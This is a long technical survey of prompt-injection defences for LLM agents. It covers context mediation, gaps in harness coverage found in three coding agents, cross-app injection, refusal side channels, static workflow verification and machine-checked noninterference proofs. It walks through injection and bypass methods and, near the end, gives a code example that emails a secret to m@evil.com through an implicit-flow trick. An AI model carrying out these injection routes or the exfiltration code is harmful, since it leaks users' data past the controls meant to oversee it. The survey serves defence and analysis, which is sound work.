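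Mediated reads are the context-channel property in its exact form. The earlier formula required every outside text x to enter by the single route K. Mediated reads add a condition on timing. If allow(x) means that the monitor approved the read that fetched x, then:

eᵢ = add(x, r) and x ∈ Out  ⇒  r = K, and eⱼ = allow(x) for some j < i

In Dongol's model, the monitor decides whether to admit outside text based on the source's name and the monitor's own state, not the text itself. It can withdraw write_file in the same step, so the tool is already unavailable when the text arrives. A Dogwood fence that matches responses instead of requests may take effect only after the text has arrived.

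A session is fresh only if everything the model retains from untrusted text has been cleared, including anything stored outside the visible conversation. An agent that saves notes for later meets this condition only if the notes are also cleared or come back through the monitor as untrusted reads. A channel can be treated as trusted only if an attacker can't write to it. A calendar that accepts invitations from outsiders doesn't qualify, even if it belongs to the user.

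The other three assumptions are that a trusted interpreter runs the plan, that a refused request has no effect the attacker can see, and that the attacker can't observe the monitor's state or the agent's internal steps. Even showing the user a reply breaks the last assumption if the reply loads an image from the attacker's server.

AgentDojo's harness checks and executes every call and every fetch itself, so it satisfies both complete mediation and mediated reads. Many defences get their best results on AgentDojo, where the harness already provides this coverage. Developers have to establish it separately for a coding agent with a shell, an unmonitored browser or a long-term memory.

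### Where text gets in

Tool results are the obvious entrance to the context, but there are at least seven others:

| Entrance | Why a harness may miss it | What it takes to route it through one check |
|---|---|---|
| Tool results | Some arrive through a shell command or browser | Label every result by its source before it enters the context |
| Error messages | They look like the system's own words but can quote outside text | Treat the error text as a tool result, or replace it with a fixed code |
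| Tool descriptions | An outside server writes them and can change them during a conversation | Keep an approved copy and check every change |
| Retrieved documents | The harness may add them without any tool call | Make retrieval request a read, and keep each passage's source |
| Persistent memory | The agent wrote the note, perhaps from a stranger's text | Save the label with the note and restore both together |
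| Resumed transcripts | They load as an earlier part of the conversation | Store them where the agent can't write, and restore labels and fences too |
| Messages from sub-agents | The sub-agent may have read untrusted text | Pass on its label, and record the sender outside the message |
| The monitor's refusals | The monitor is trusted, but its answer may depend on protected data | Use fixed wording that reveals nothing about that data |

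All outside text passes through the part of the harness that assembles the model's input. A check there covers text from every source, but the record of where a passage came from may be lost by then. Checks at each source can use that information, but they miss text from any source the developers overlooked. A harness can combine the two by labeling text at its source and treating any text that reaches the assembly step without a label as untrusted.

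### Where actions get out

The exits raise a similar problem, because a tool list describes only some of the ways in which an agent can act:

| Exit | What it takes to route it through one check |
|---|---|
| Declared tools | Send every call through the policy engine, including calls to tool servers on the same computer |
| The shell | Enforce limits in the operating system on every program the shell starts |
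| Background and scheduled jobs | Apply the same limits after the original call has ended |
| Sub-agents | Give each one the parent's prompt class and history, or a stricter class |
| Rendered links and images | Stop automatic loading, or check each address as a network request |

Many harnesses check calls with a wrapper, a piece of code placed around each tool. *Stop Means Stop* (2026) points out that this coverage is only a convention, because a developer who forgets to wrap a tool leaves it unchecked. If the operating system forces network traffic through the gate, an unwrapped tool's network request fails. Files, shared memory and messages between processes each need a similar barrier.

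*AgentBouncer* (2026) applies one check to shell commands by intercepting their system calls, which are a program's requests to the operating system's kernel, such as to open a file or start a process. Ordinary code intercepts each system call during a tool's run, and AgentBouncer decides whether to allow it before the kernel carries it out. A prepared profile settles the familiar requests, and a language model judges whether the rest are safe and necessary for the task.

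### Tests on three coding agents

*Ring-0 by Default*, by Li and colleagues, provides the broadest evidence on how deployed agents handle these routes. The title refers to the most privileged level of an operating system. Li and colleagues looked in today's agents for counterparts to 116 mechanisms from operating-system textbooks. They found that 65 were missing, 11 worked much as they do in an operating system, and 14 existed in a changed form. The remaining 26 were "degraded", meaning that the function exists but its protection depends on the model following instructions or on a check that another path bypasses. Li and colleagues consider this category the most dangerous because the system appears to be protected.

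Most of these verdicts rest on documentation and analysis. Thirteen experiments on Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI tested 25 of the mechanisms. In some runs, a script issued the tool calls in place of the model, which showed what the harness would permit whatever a model did. In others, a real model chose the actions. Sixteen mechanisms behaved as the analysis had predicted, seven needed a more precise description, and two turned out to be degraded rather than missing.

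The experiments showed that access checks applied to individual tools, not to the whole process. With permission prompts off, one agent's file tool still refused to write outside the project folder, but its shell could write there. In all five runs with a real model, the model ended up using the shell, four times after the file tool had refused. Similarly, two agents' built-in web-fetching tools checked the network destination, but their shells did not. In its default mode, Codex CLI also applies a kernel sandbox, which can restrict a shell.

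Text could also enter the context unchecked in several ways. All three agents trusted their saved transcripts when resuming a session, and in every run they loaded a correctly formatted forged record as a message from the user. Notes an agent wrote to its memory files came back as instructions in the next session's input. Deleting such a file didn't fully remove the note, because the transcript still held a copy.

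Sub-agents had the same write access as their parents in all 45 runs. When a sub-agent put a false sender name in its report, two of the three harnesses altered or enclosed the text so that the name couldn't pass for a real label. In the third, the parent model had no way to tell the false name from a real label.

Li and colleagues have notified the vendors. They don't regard the forged transcript as an exploit in itself, because it requires write access to the user's files. But agents often have that access, and two of the three agents could rewrite their own transcripts when permission prompts were off. Hostile text that influences an agent in one session could then return with the user's authority in the next.

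The experiments cover one model, specific product versions and runs without the interactive interface. Each real-model test had five runs per setting, so even five out of five is compatible with a true rate as low as 57%. The scripted runs are firmer evidence because they test the harness directly.

### A context shared by many apps

ChatGPT lets many third-party apps write to one context. Wang and colleagues found hidden system-priority messages there, but these relied on undocumented options that OpenAI could remove. The larger problem is that the conversation is one flat sequence, with no reliable record of which app contributed what. Text from one app stays in the conversation and can influence how the model uses another app.

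The attack also worked without the undocumented options. In tests on six models available in May 2026, an app's ordinary follow-up message was enough to change what the model asked a second app to do, although one model needed different wording. On GPT-5.5 Thinking, the researchers confirmed two more routes for the attack, through the description of an app's tool and through a suggested reply that the user sends without seeing all of it. The harness also let structured tool results reach the model, but the model's training led it to ignore the planted instructions in every variant they tried.

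Removing the follow-up function would break useful apps without solving the problem. Of the 888 apps in the catalogue, 75 used it, for instance to have the model summarise a result. Wang and colleagues propose giving each app its own context. The platform would start that context with a summary of what the user wants, keep the app's messages inside it, and inspect the result before passing it to the main conversation.

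They acknowledge that no known technique makes the return path completely safe. An operating system can check the sender and type of a message without interpreting its contents, but a model has to read free text to judge whether it contains an instruction, and the text may influence that model. This limit applies when free text has to reach the main model. A platform could instead return typed answers or stored variables, as FIDES does, but the main model could then no longer compare and combine the apps' results freely, which is much of the reason for sharing a context.

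Wang and colleagues reported the follow-up function and its undocumented options to OpenAI on 9 March 2026. OpenAI classified the report as outside its bounty programme, where prompt injection counted as a model behaviour issue. The options were still accessible in May.

### What a refusal can reveal

When a monitor blocks a call, it usually returns a refusal to the agent, which adds new text to the context. *Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) describes how this refusal can leak information. For example, hostile text might lead an agent to request a protected file. The monitor blocks the request and no data comes back, but if the refusal reads "permission denied" where a missing file would have produced "not found", it reveals that the file exists. The agent can then pass this on in a later message to an outsider.

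Labels on data don't track what a refusal reveals, because a refused call returns nothing to label. One refusal may reveal very little, but n requests with two possible outcomes each can reveal up to n bits, which may be enough to work out what a system holds and how it is protected.

Chinaei's monitor, ARM, adds refused calls to its graph of where data came from. It links each refusal to the next tool call and blocks any call that such a link reaches. Nobody can observe whether a refusal influenced the model, so ARM treats each one as if it did. In a test of three attack scenarios, ARM blocked all three, while a simpler provenance check blocked none.

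Chinaei accepts that the assumption will stop some harmless calls. Applied literally, the rule blocks the next call, whatever it is, and because that block is another refusal, it could stall the rest of the session. Three attack scenarios can't show how often this would happen in ordinary work.

A less disruptive remedy is to return the same response for a forbidden file as for a missing one. The agent then can't find out whether the file exists, but it also can't explain to the user why the task failed. Nor can the system refuse actions silently. Hempel and colleagues note that Kairos must tell the agent when it discards a held action, or the agent will continue as if the action had taken place.

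Dongol's assumption about refusals concerns what the attacker sees directly, for example in a log, so it doesn't fully cover this leak. His framework leaves out models that use the monitor's answers to decide when to obey an injected instruction.

### Memory that returns handles

Persistent memory combines several of these problems, because outside text can enter in one session, sit unused for weeks, and influence an action after any temporary restriction has expired. *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) keeps such text away from the main model even after the agent has saved it.

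PerMIT trusts only what the user typed and the exact values the user confirmed. Everything a tool returns, including errors and status messages, goes into an untrusted store. The main model can read the trusted store, but for everything else it receives only handles, which are names that reveal nothing about the content. A quarantined model searches the untrusted store and also returns only handles.

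In the paper's example, a user has the agent look up a dentist online, and one page contains an instruction to forward the user's saved files to an attacker. The main model receives only an acknowledgement. In a later session, the user asks the agent to email the dentist's number to a relative. The agent asks the quarantined model for the number, receives a handle, and passes it to the email tool. Before the email is sent, the harness shows the user the exact text behind the handle, so the user can reject it if it is the planted instruction instead of the phone number. Accepting the text creates a trusted copy and leaves the original untrusted.

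The memory interface can send the main model only an acknowledgement, a handle, a fixed failure message, the user's decision to accept or reject, or text from the trusted store. A search returns the same kind of handle whether it succeeds, finds nothing or fails. This closes most of the channel that Chinaei describes, although a rejection still passes the user's decision to the agent.

Jiang and colleagues prove two theorems about this design. Action Integrity concerns the values that reach sensitive tools. Let Typed be the set of values the user typed, and Confirmed the set of pairs of an exact value and the tool for which the user approved it. For every sensitive tool t and every value v in its arguments a:

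exec(t, a)  ⇒  v ∈ Typed or (v, t) ∈ Confirmed

Reasoning Integrity concerns the agent's behaviour as a whole. Take two runs, ρ₁ and ρ₂, with the same starting state, user input, random choices and schedule, but any differences in their untrusted text. Let D(ρ) be everything the confirmation screens showed, together with the user's decisions, and let B(ρ) be the main model's operations, its tool calls and the replies it received. Then:

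D(ρ₁) = D(ρ₂)  ⇒  B(ρ₁) = B(ρ₂)

Hidden text can therefore influence the agent only through what appears on the confirmation screen. The proof checker Lean has verified both theorems for one user's memory and for runs of any length. It hasn't verified some features that handle values in batches, or that a deployed harness matches the model in the proof. The theorems also don't cover information that leaks through timing.

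The protection depends on the person or model that confirms each value. Action Integrity assumes that every approval matches what the user intended. An approval covers a value and a tool rather than a single call, so a value approved for one email can go into another without being confirmed again. Two values that are harmless separately may also be harmful together. An option for sharing memories between users weakens the protection further, because an entry that enough people have confirmed becomes available to others without another check.

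Jiang and colleagues tested PerMIT on Trojan Hippo, a benchmark in which one tool result plants an instruction that takes effect in a later session. When the gate approved everything, attacks succeeded between 0% and 10% of the time, depending on the model. None succeeded when a language model decided what to approve. But that model has to read the untrusted text, and the researchers haven't tested attacks designed to mislead it.

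### Establishing coverage in a product

To show that a product has no unchecked path, a vendor can start from effects instead of tool names. *Metis* (2026) notes that tools with different checks can produce the same effect, so a gate has to report which paths it covers. *CONTINUITY* (2026) proposes that a deployment list the effects it protects and send every interface that can produce them through one broker. Its test system includes a direct path around the broker as a control. The protected effect went ahead on that path even though every mechanism on the normal path was working correctly.

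*CONTINUITY*'s control also suggests testing a real product by attempting, for each kind of effect, an action that should fail. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) sets out such tests for files, the shell, the network, code repositories, memory and delegation to other agents. The paper's guarantee does not cover any route that a deployment leaves outside the gate.

A vendor's gate can't log calls that never reach it, so something other than the gate has to record what happened. *guardscope* (Toyoda, Leung and U, 2026) uses a sensor in the operating system's kernel. The software runs a fixed set of actions without a language model, then compares the sensor's record with the gate's decisions. It classifies each action as checked, bypassed, or prevented by some other barrier. Before measuring anything, it confirms that the gate is working by sending an action that the gate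 must refuse.

One analysis lists 15 paths by which an agent can act and eight deployment designs, ranging from no check to a check in the kernel. In that analysis, a gateway for remote tool servers reliably covers only one path, and a check built into the harness covers five. Five paths, including processes that keep running after a call ends and jobs handed to a scheduler, bypass every check above the kernel, so adding another gateway doesn't help with them.

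A check in the kernel could in principle cover at least 13 of the 15 paths, but the low-level events it monitors, such as a program opening a file, don't identify the tool or conversation responsible. It can block every process from accessing .env, but on its own it can't allow write_file for a maintainer and deny it to a visitor. Coverage also depends on which events the product monitors. The one kernel-level product in the tests checked 7 of 15 actions and missed all seven tool calls. Toyoda and colleagues therefore recommend combining a check in the harness with one in the kernel. Their test actions used only four of the 15 paths, so the figures for the other 11 come from analysis. An action counted as "checked" may also have received the wrong decision.

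This method measures actions, but a similar test could cover incoming text. A tester would put a different harmless marker in each source of incoming text, such as an error message, a tool description, a saved note and a sub-agent's report. The tester would then record everything the harness sends to the model and compare it with the context channel's log. If a marker reached the model without a matching log entry, text from that source had bypassed the check. The test could find gaps but not prove that there are none, because a summary can reword a marker and the tester may then miss it. Li and colleagues already ran each agent through a relay between the harness and the model, and the recording would take place at that relay.

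A product's test results would apply only to the version and configuration tested. The vendor would have to repeat the tests for each release, and a customer who connects a new tool server would need to test the paths it adds for tool calls and incoming text.

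## What can be checked before the agent runs

Static verification examines every path that a workflow permits, without running the model, whereas a test for unchecked paths covers only the paths that the testers try. Static verification needs a written description of the agent's steps and the permitted moves between them. Many developers already produce one, because frameworks such as LangGraph and CrewAI have them build an agent from named steps with explicit connections.

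### A workflow as a graph

Xavier, Jolly and colleagues (2026), in *Agentproof*, describe a tool that extracts these connections from programs written in four frameworks. In slightly simplified notation, it represents a workflow as:

G = (V, E, κ, T, v₀, F)

V is the set of nodes (the workflow's steps), and E is the set of edges (the permitted moves between steps). The function κ gives each node a type, such as tool, model, router or human approval, and marks each edge as direct, conditional, parallel or part of a loop. T(v) is the set of tools declared for node v. Every run starts at the entry node v₀ and should finish at one of the exit nodes in F.

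Suppose the triage project rebuilds its agent as the following workflow:

```
start → read → sort
sort  → quote → draft → reply → end
sort  → fix → approve → write → end
```

Four of the nodes have one tool each: `read` has `read_issue`, `quote` has `read_file`, `reply` has `post_comment`, and `write` has `write_file`. The router at `sort` sends bug reports down the first branch and typo reports down the second. A model drafts the correction at `fix`, and a maintainer reviews it at `approve`.

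A router's choice often comes from a model, so prompt injection can influence it. The analysis therefore treats every edge out of the router as possible. If it finds no path to a tool, the agent can't call that tool even when hostile text determines every choice the model makes, provided the harness restricts each step to its declared tools and edges.

### Searching for a way around the approval

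The project wants a maintainer to approve every file change. To check this, Agentproof deletes the human-approval nodes from the graph and looks for tools it can still reach. It uses breadth-first search, which visits the entry node, then every node one move away, then every node two moves away, and stops when it finds nothing new. With approve deleted, the search visits these nodes:

| Moves from start | Nodes reached |
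|---|---|
| 0 | start |
| 1 | read |
| 2 | sort |
| 3 | quote, fix |
| 4 | draft |
| 5 | reply |
| 6 | end |

The search cannot continue past fix on the second branch, so it never reaches write. Any path that avoided approve would still exist after the deletion, so every path to write_file must pass through approve.

Now suppose a developer adds an edge from fix straight to write, to save maintainers from approving one-letter corrections. The same search then reaches write in four moves, and Agentproof reports the path:

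start → read → sort → fix → write

A test run would expose this gap only if the test issue happened to trigger the shortcut.

### A rule about order

The fence "no write_file after read_issue" depends on earlier events, so it needs a different search. An automaton like Schneider's can track those events, with a third state for a violation:

| State | Meaning | Event that changes it |
|---|---|---|
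| q₀ | No issue read | read_issue leads to q₁ |
| q₁ | An issue has been read | write_file leads to q₂ |
| q₂ | The rule is broken | None |

Agentproof can combine the automaton with the graph in advance. The search then moves through pairs of a node and a state, and the workflow can break the rule if the search reaches any pair containing q₂. In the original triage workflow, without the shortcut, it does (each pair gives the state after the node has run):

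(start, q₀) → (read, q₁) → (sort, q₁) → (fix, q₁) → (approve, q₁) → (write, q₂)

The approval makes no difference here. Every run reads an issue before it does anything else, so every write breaks the rule, and the project has to change the workflow itself. It could move the router to the front and have it separate public issues from typo fixes that maintainers request:

```
start → sort
sort  → read → quote → draft → reply → end
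sort  → fix → approve → write → end
```

The search now reaches write only in state q₀, so the workflow passes. If a developer later adds an edge from reply back to sort, so that one run can handle several requests, the search finds a violation again, because the run can read an issue on its first pass and write a file on its second. If the harness clears the context between requests, the developer can add a "context cleared" event that returns the automaton to q₀.

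As with any fence, the result doesn't cover a stranger's text that enters by another route, such as the request that starts the run.

With |V| nodes and |Q| states, the search visits at most |V| × |Q| pairs, which is 30 for the triage workflow. Xavier and colleagues prove that if the search finds no violation, no run that follows the graph can break the rule. A violation it does find may be a false alarm, because some paths in the graph may be impossible in practice. Xavier and colleagues haven't measured how many false alarms this causes.

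Agentproof's rule language can't express this fence directly. It has seven forms, such as "never a" and "after a, b must follow before a happens again", but none for "never b after a". The closest combination, "never read_issue or never write_file", also forbids harmless writes before the first read. To get the exact rule, the project would have to build the automaton by hand.

### What 18 workflows can show

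Xavier and colleagues tested Agentproof on 18 workflows they had written themselves, each with 5 to 12 nodes. Five (27%) had structural defects, such as a loop with no exit or a missing edge that means the agent drafts an email but never sends it. Ten (55%) failed a policy that requires human approval.

The researchers deliberately included known mistakes, so these percentages don't indicate how common such defects are in deployed agents. The human-approval figure comes from a simpler check than the search above. A workflow passes if it contains a human node anywhere, even if the approval is on the wrong branch. The researchers consider some of the ten failures debatable because low-risk tasks may not need approval.

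The team also wrote 15 rules about the order of events, and all of them fit the seven forms. This is weak evidence that the forms are sufficient, because the same people designed the language. The static search found that an email draft could go ahead without the required human review, a violation that ten random simulated runs per workflow had missed.

Speed is not a problem. On an artificial graph with 5,000 nodes, the structural checks took about 105 milliseconds.

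### Bugs in real workflows

*Automated Safety Analysis for Agentic Workflows* (Chen, Li and colleagues, 2026) provides better evidence about real projects. The researchers collected 861 problem reports from 13 frameworks and traced 783 of them to how developers had connected the parts of a workflow. These bugs can cause harm without an attacker. In one incident, a loop between agents had no exit condition and ran up a $47,000 bill.

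About three-quarters of the bugs can't be detected from the graph's nodes and edges alone. For example, two parallel steps may write to the same variable, and whether one result erases the other depends on how the framework merges them. The researchers' analyser, APSIS, therefore adds labels for such behaviour to the graph and searches it for twelve kinds of bug. Two of these directly concern tool limits. In one, a coordinator that should only assign work has tools of its own, and in the other, human approvals come at the wrong point.

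The researchers tested APSIS on 135 faulty workflows and the corrected version of each:

| Method | Faulty workflows flagged | Corrected workflows flagged |
|---|---|---|
| APSIS | 84% | 8% |
| CodeQL, a general code analyser | 7% | 3% |
| Three language models | 77% to 88% | 49% to 67% |
| The frameworks' own checks | 0% | 0% |

Without the behavioural labels, APSIS found only 50% of the bugs. With them, 91% of its warnings were correct in this test, where half of the workflows were faulty. If only 5% of a company's workflows had such a bug, about 36% of the warnings would be correct at the same detection rates.

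The benchmark and the bug categories come from the same collection of reports, so a search for new bugs is a fairer test of APSIS. Chen and colleagues ran it on more than 40 open-source projects and found 36 previously unknown bugs in 21 repositories. The maintainers have fixed 33 and confirmed the other three.

About half of the 36 involved shared state, and some of those could undermine a safety limit. In a project called OctoBot, runs stored their identifiers in one shared slot, so a person's approval could resume the wrong run. Agentproof's search would not catch this, because the approval node can be on every path to the tool even when the approval belongs to a different run.

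### A free loop permits everything

These checks help only if developers have divided the tools among different nodes. An agent like Codex instead has a single loop in which the model can choose any tool at every step:

start → model ⇄ tools → end

If the triage agent works this way, the tools node holds all four tools. The search reaches write_file in two moves, and the automaton reaches q₂ on the second pass through the loop. Both findings are correct but of little use, because this graph permits calls in any order. The analysis can rule out only tools that are missing from the node's list, and reading the list would give the same result.

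Dantas and colleagues conclude that static analysis works only on finite workflows specified in advance, whereas most realistic agents plan as they go. *Backtracking Agent Applications Security Incidents* (2026) describes a related difficulty for people investigating attacks on such agents, who generally can't tell from the program's code which tool brought in the malicious data.

A project can keep some of the flexibility by putting a smaller loop inside one node, where the model could choose freely among read_issue, read_file and post_comment. The write_file tool would stay in a separate node that requires a maintainer's approval. The graph would not specify the order of calls inside the loop, but the search could still establish that no run goes from the loop to write_file without that approval. The analysis can also check a plan fixed before the run, such as ACE's.

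### When the graph and the program differ

A result about the graph applies to the program only if the two match. If the graph lacks an edge that the program has, the check can miss a real path to a tool. Extra edges can cause false alarms.

The graph checked before a run may stop matching the workflow during the run, because some frameworks let a program add agents or change the connections between steps. Someone then has to check the new graph or prevent such changes. Agentproof doesn't yet recheck the graph automatically.

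The tool can also misread the program before checking it. In 27 small tests with simulated framework objects, Agentproof found every node and edge but sometimes got a node's type wrong. For LangGraph, it identifies a human approval by looking for "human" in the node's name, so it would take the triage workflow's approve node for a model step and raise a false alarm. A model step called "humanize_reply" would cause a worse mistake, since the tool could count it as a human approval and miss an unapproved path through it.

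APSIS reduces this risk by reading the workflow object that the framework has already built and by treating any connection it can't resolve as unsafe.

Wang, Hou and colleagues (2026) tried extraction from source code on a much larger scale in *AgentFlow*. Their analyser recognises 143 programming constructs from five frameworks and builds a graph of each program's agents, prompts, tools and memory. It reported that in 238 (4.4%) of 5,399 open-source programs, text from a prompt could influence a call to a sensitive tool, such as one that sends messages or runs commands.

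The researchers then checked a sample of 100 reports by hand and found that 73 were real vulnerabilities. In 25 of the other 27, the path existed but the tool was fairly harmless, for example one that could only read from a database. They also examined 100 agents that had sensitive tools but no report, and found nine risks that the analyser had missed. The causes included tools that the program attaches while running and developers' own wrappers around commands. A tool may therefore still be reachable even if such an analyser reports nothing.

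This kind of analysis is known to miss connections. *Backtracking Agent Applications Security Incidents* reports that its static analysis can't resolve how LangChain selects the function behind a tool call, so its graph lacks the path through that call. Checking everything by hand is impractical. *Beyond Predefined Sinks* (2026) identified 23,866 places in 65 agent projects where the code might perform a security-sensitive operation, about 367 per project.

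### Following text through a model call

Taint analysis checks whether text from an untrusted source reaches a dangerous operation, which even a correct graph of the steps doesn't show. It marks the untrusted data and follows it through the code. At each function call, it must determine which inputs can affect the output, normally by analyzing the function's own code.

That fails when the function is a call to a language model, because the program's code shows only a prompt going out and text coming back. Xu, Cheng and colleagues (2026) explain in *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* that two widely used analysers, CodeQL and Semgrep, don't mark the returned text as tainted, so they lose the flow at that point. The scanner in *Agent Audit* (2026) instead treats the result of a common LangChain model call as tainted, whatever the prompt contained. This keeps the flow but can raise an alarm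 even when every input was trustworthy.

PRISM, a system by Xu and colleagues, analyzes each input separately. A program usually builds its prompt from a template with placeholders, which it fills with values such as an issue's text. PRISM uses 25 labels to describe what happened to each value in the model's output. The labels cover how much of the value survived, from an exact copy down to a single yes or no, and whether it appeared as prose, structured data or something executable.

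Four of the labels mean that the value didn't get through: the model ignored it, lacked the necessary context, lacked the necessary capability, or refused on policy grounds. Let N be the set of these four labels and L(p) the set of labels for placeholder p. Then:

reach(p) ⇔ L(p) ⊄ N

o is tainted ⇔ for some i, pᵢ is tainted and reach(pᵢ)

If the triage program asks a model to summarise issue 42, the issue's text gets a label for summaries. That label isn't in N, so the summary is tainted, and ordinary analysis can then trace it to post_comment.

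To assign the labels, the researchers ran prompts from real programs and had three language models compare each value with the output. They kept a label if at least two models agreed on it. Of 8,119 values, 7% had only labels from N.

They then tested the method on 353 pairs of a placeholder and a dangerous operation, such as running code or querying a database. Human reviewers had judged that an attacker's text could get from one to the other in 110 of the pairs. PRISM used its labels for the model call and a language model to trace the rest of the path through the code:

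| Method | Reported flows that were real | Real flows found | F₁ score |
|---|---|---|---|
| Treat all model output as tainted | 31.2% | 100% | 47.5% |
| Best language model without the labels | 58.1% | 68.2% | 62.8% |
| PRISM, best version | 72.5% | 93.6% | 81.7% |

The F₁ score combines the other two columns, and PRISM's is clearly the best of the three. PRISM would save a developer looking for bugs a lot of time. But missed flows matter more than false alarms when the goal is to show that a tool is unreachable. PRISM missed about 6% of the real flows, and only the crude rule in the first row found them all.

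The labels also depend on how the model treated particular values, and an attacker can choose different values. In tests on six vulnerabilities in OpenClaw, an open-source agent, PRISM correctly classified the program before and after each fix. After one fix, the model refused the malicious request, so PRISM counted the path as blocked. But the code path from the model's output to the command remained, and a differently worded attack might get past the refusal. Xu and colleagues claim only that their method is sound if the labels are right. A project that needs a guarantee still has to treat everything the model produces from untrusted text as tainted, and accept the extra false alarms.

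## What machine-checked proofs establish

Nobody can prove what a language model will output next, but a proof about an agent doesn't have to predict the model. It can let the model output anything and rely only on the rules the harness follows. If M is any function from a context to an output, and H(M) is the harness running with that model, the theorem has the form:

for every M, every run of H(M) satisfies P

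Tool unreachability is easy to prove this way. Suppose only one line of the harness can execute a tool, and the test t ∈ A(c) comes immediately before it. Then t runs only if it is in A(c), whatever the model returns. This is true at every step, so it holds for the whole run. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) likewise treats the model as an adversary that may make any choice, and calls this the strongest stance available to a method that doesn't depend on the model's internals.

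Proving that an agent doesn't leak information is harder, because the proof has to compare several possible runs. Two projects from 2026 have done so with proof assistants, programs that check every step of a mathematical proof. In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands present LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, and prove in Lean that it enforces a form of noninterference. In *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, Dongol uses Isabelle/HOL to compare an agent under attack with the same agent when its model ignores injected instructions.

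### Noninterference when the model is random

Write d₁ ≈ d₂ when two inputs differ only in ways that a given observer may not see. For a program without randomness, noninterference means:

d₁ ≈ d₂  ⇒  run(d₁) ≈ run(d₂)

The formula covers both parts of a label. For confidentiality, the observer sees public data and the inputs differ in a secret, such as the contents of .env. For integrity, the observer sees only trusted data and the inputs differ in the text of issue 42. In that case, the formula means the stranger's text can't change anything the system counts as trusted.

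A language model picks its output partly at random, so the same input can lead to different results. To show that protected data doesn't affect what an observer sees, a proof can require every visible outcome to be equally likely for any two inputs that differ only in that data. But a harness that blocks forbidden calls sometimes stops a run, and whether it stops can depend on protected data. Most security proofs therefore use a weaker, termination-insensitive requirement, which allows protected data to influence whether the program finishes but nothing else.

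Combining randomness with this exception takes some care. Let μ₁(o) and μ₂(o) be the probabilities of a visible outcome o for the two inputs. They may add up to less than 1, because some runs never finish. Garby and colleagues call μ₁ and μ₂ compatible if there is a third set of probabilities ω such that:

μ₁(o) ≤ ω(o) and μ₂(o) ≤ ω(o) for every o, and the sum of all ω(o) is at most 1

Suppose an agent posts one of two public replies, and a file it has read contains either secret s₁ or secret s₂:

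| Outcome | Probability with s₁ | Probability with s₂ | Larger of the two |
|---|---|---|---|
| Posts "confirmed" | 0.6 | 0.5 | 0.6 |
| Posts "duplicate" | 0.3 | 0.4 | 0.4 |
| Never finishes | 0.1 | 0.1 | Not counted |

The larger values add up to exactly 1, so the two cases are compatible. The unfinished runs could account for the whole difference. If every run finished, with probabilities of 0.7 and 0.3 in one case and 0.6 and 0.4 in the other, the larger values would add up to 1.1 and no ω would exist. If a program always finishes, the two cases are therefore compatible only when they are equal. In general, the statistical distance between the two cases is at most the average of their probabilities of not finishing, which is 10 percentage points here.

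### A language in which every value has a label

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language in which programs consist of functions. Every value carries a label for integrity and confidentiality, and so does the conversation, the list of messages exchanged with the model. As in FIDES, sending a message adds its label to the conversation's, and the model's response gets the combined label. If the response is code, it runs under that label too, so the label on hostile text still applies to any program the text causes the model to write.

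Two commands control what the model reads. The command "clear" empties the conversation, and "fork" runs part of a program in a temporary copy of the conversation and then restores the original. Together they can express a quarantined model in one line. In slightly simplified notation, the triage agent could contain:

```
let issue = ["U"]:"text of issue 42" in
let summary = fork (let _ = clear in @("Summarise: " + issue)) in
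post_comment summary
```

Here "U" means untrusted and @ queries the model. The model reads the issue only in the temporary copy, so the main conversation stays trusted, but the summary is untrusted. Tools can check labels with an "assert" command, which stops the run if a value's label is too restrictive. A write_file function that asserts its text is trusted would reject the summary. CaMeL and FIDES build the split between two models into their architecture, whereas an LLMbda program can create such a split wherever one is needed.

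The main theorem covers every program in the language. Let C₀ and C₁ be two conversations, and e₀ and e₁ two programs together with their data. For every level m at which someone might observe the system:

C₀ ≈ₘ C₁ and e₀ ≈ₘ e₁  ⇒  the outcomes visible at level m are compatible

This includes agents that write and run their own code, and agents whose model chooses one tool call at a time. By comparison, Costa and colleagues' theorem for FIDES covers a single planning loop.

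The proof constructs the ω that the definition requires by running the program under altered rules and taking the resulting outcome probabilities. These rules skip a computation as soon as its label rises above m and substitute an empty value. The altered run never uses the protected data, so its probabilities are the same for both starting points. It also produces each visible outcome at least as often as the real program does, because a skipped computation can't fail.

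### Endorsement that can't release secrets

An agent sometimes has to act on an untrusted value, such as a category that a quarantined model has read off an issue. LLMbda's "endorse" command can mark the value as trusted. If the value's label is ℓ, the requested label is r, and pc is the label of the data that caused the program to reach this point, then:

new label = pc ⊔ (integrity of r, confidentiality of ℓ)

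The confidentiality part never becomes less strict. Joining in pc prevents "endorse" from making anything trusted inside code that runs because of untrusted data.

By design, endorsement breaks noninterference for integrity, because the attacker can now influence a value that counts as trusted. A second theorem shows that the main theorem still holds for every observer who ignores integrity, as long as the two parts of the label are independent. Even if an attacker chooses all the untrusted inputs and the program endorses every one, no secret reaches a public output. If the triage agent endorsed a file path taken from issue 42, it could go to the wrong file, but the contents of .env would keep their secret label.

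The theorem does not protect against a false value that the program has endorsed. The only two attacks that succeeded against the LLMbda test agent relied on such values. The language can't check whether an endorsement was wise, but a reviewer can find every place where one occurs.

### The verified program is the harness

Garby and colleagues wrote LLMbda's interpreter in Lean, which is both a programming language and a proof checker, so their theorems apply to the program itself. Proofs about software often cover only a mathematical description, and programmers may make mistakes when they implement it. When an agent runs, the same interpreter tracks the labels and calls the model. A third theorem shows that the interpreter's results occur with exactly the probabilities that the language's rules give. Any agent written in LLMbda therefore gets the guarantees without a proof of its own. Garby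 and colleagues know of no earlier harness of this kind.

The proof does not cover the whole system. The network request to the model is unverified code, which the theorems treat as an unknown function. They also assume that each response depends only on chance and the conversation that the interpreter sends. This assumption would fail if a model provider kept memory between requests, because "clear" would no longer remove everything the model had read. The theory also assumes that tools and data sources are part of the LLMbda program, but in the tests, a Python layer copied the state of a simulated bank into the program and the results back out.

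### A secret revealed by a branch not taken

Garby and colleagues also examined CaMeL, whose developers had left a formal treatment to later work. Suppose an injected instruction tries to reveal whether a customer's balance is above a threshold by sending an email only if it is. CaMeL blocks this direct attempt, because anything that runs inside a branch on a secret gets the secret's label. The following program uses two variables to avoid that rule:

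```
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL updates a variable's label only when an assignment runs:

| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
| First "if" | tmp becomes False and secret | Skipped, so tmp stays True and public |
| Second "if" | Skipped, so rich stays True and public | rich becomes False and stays public |
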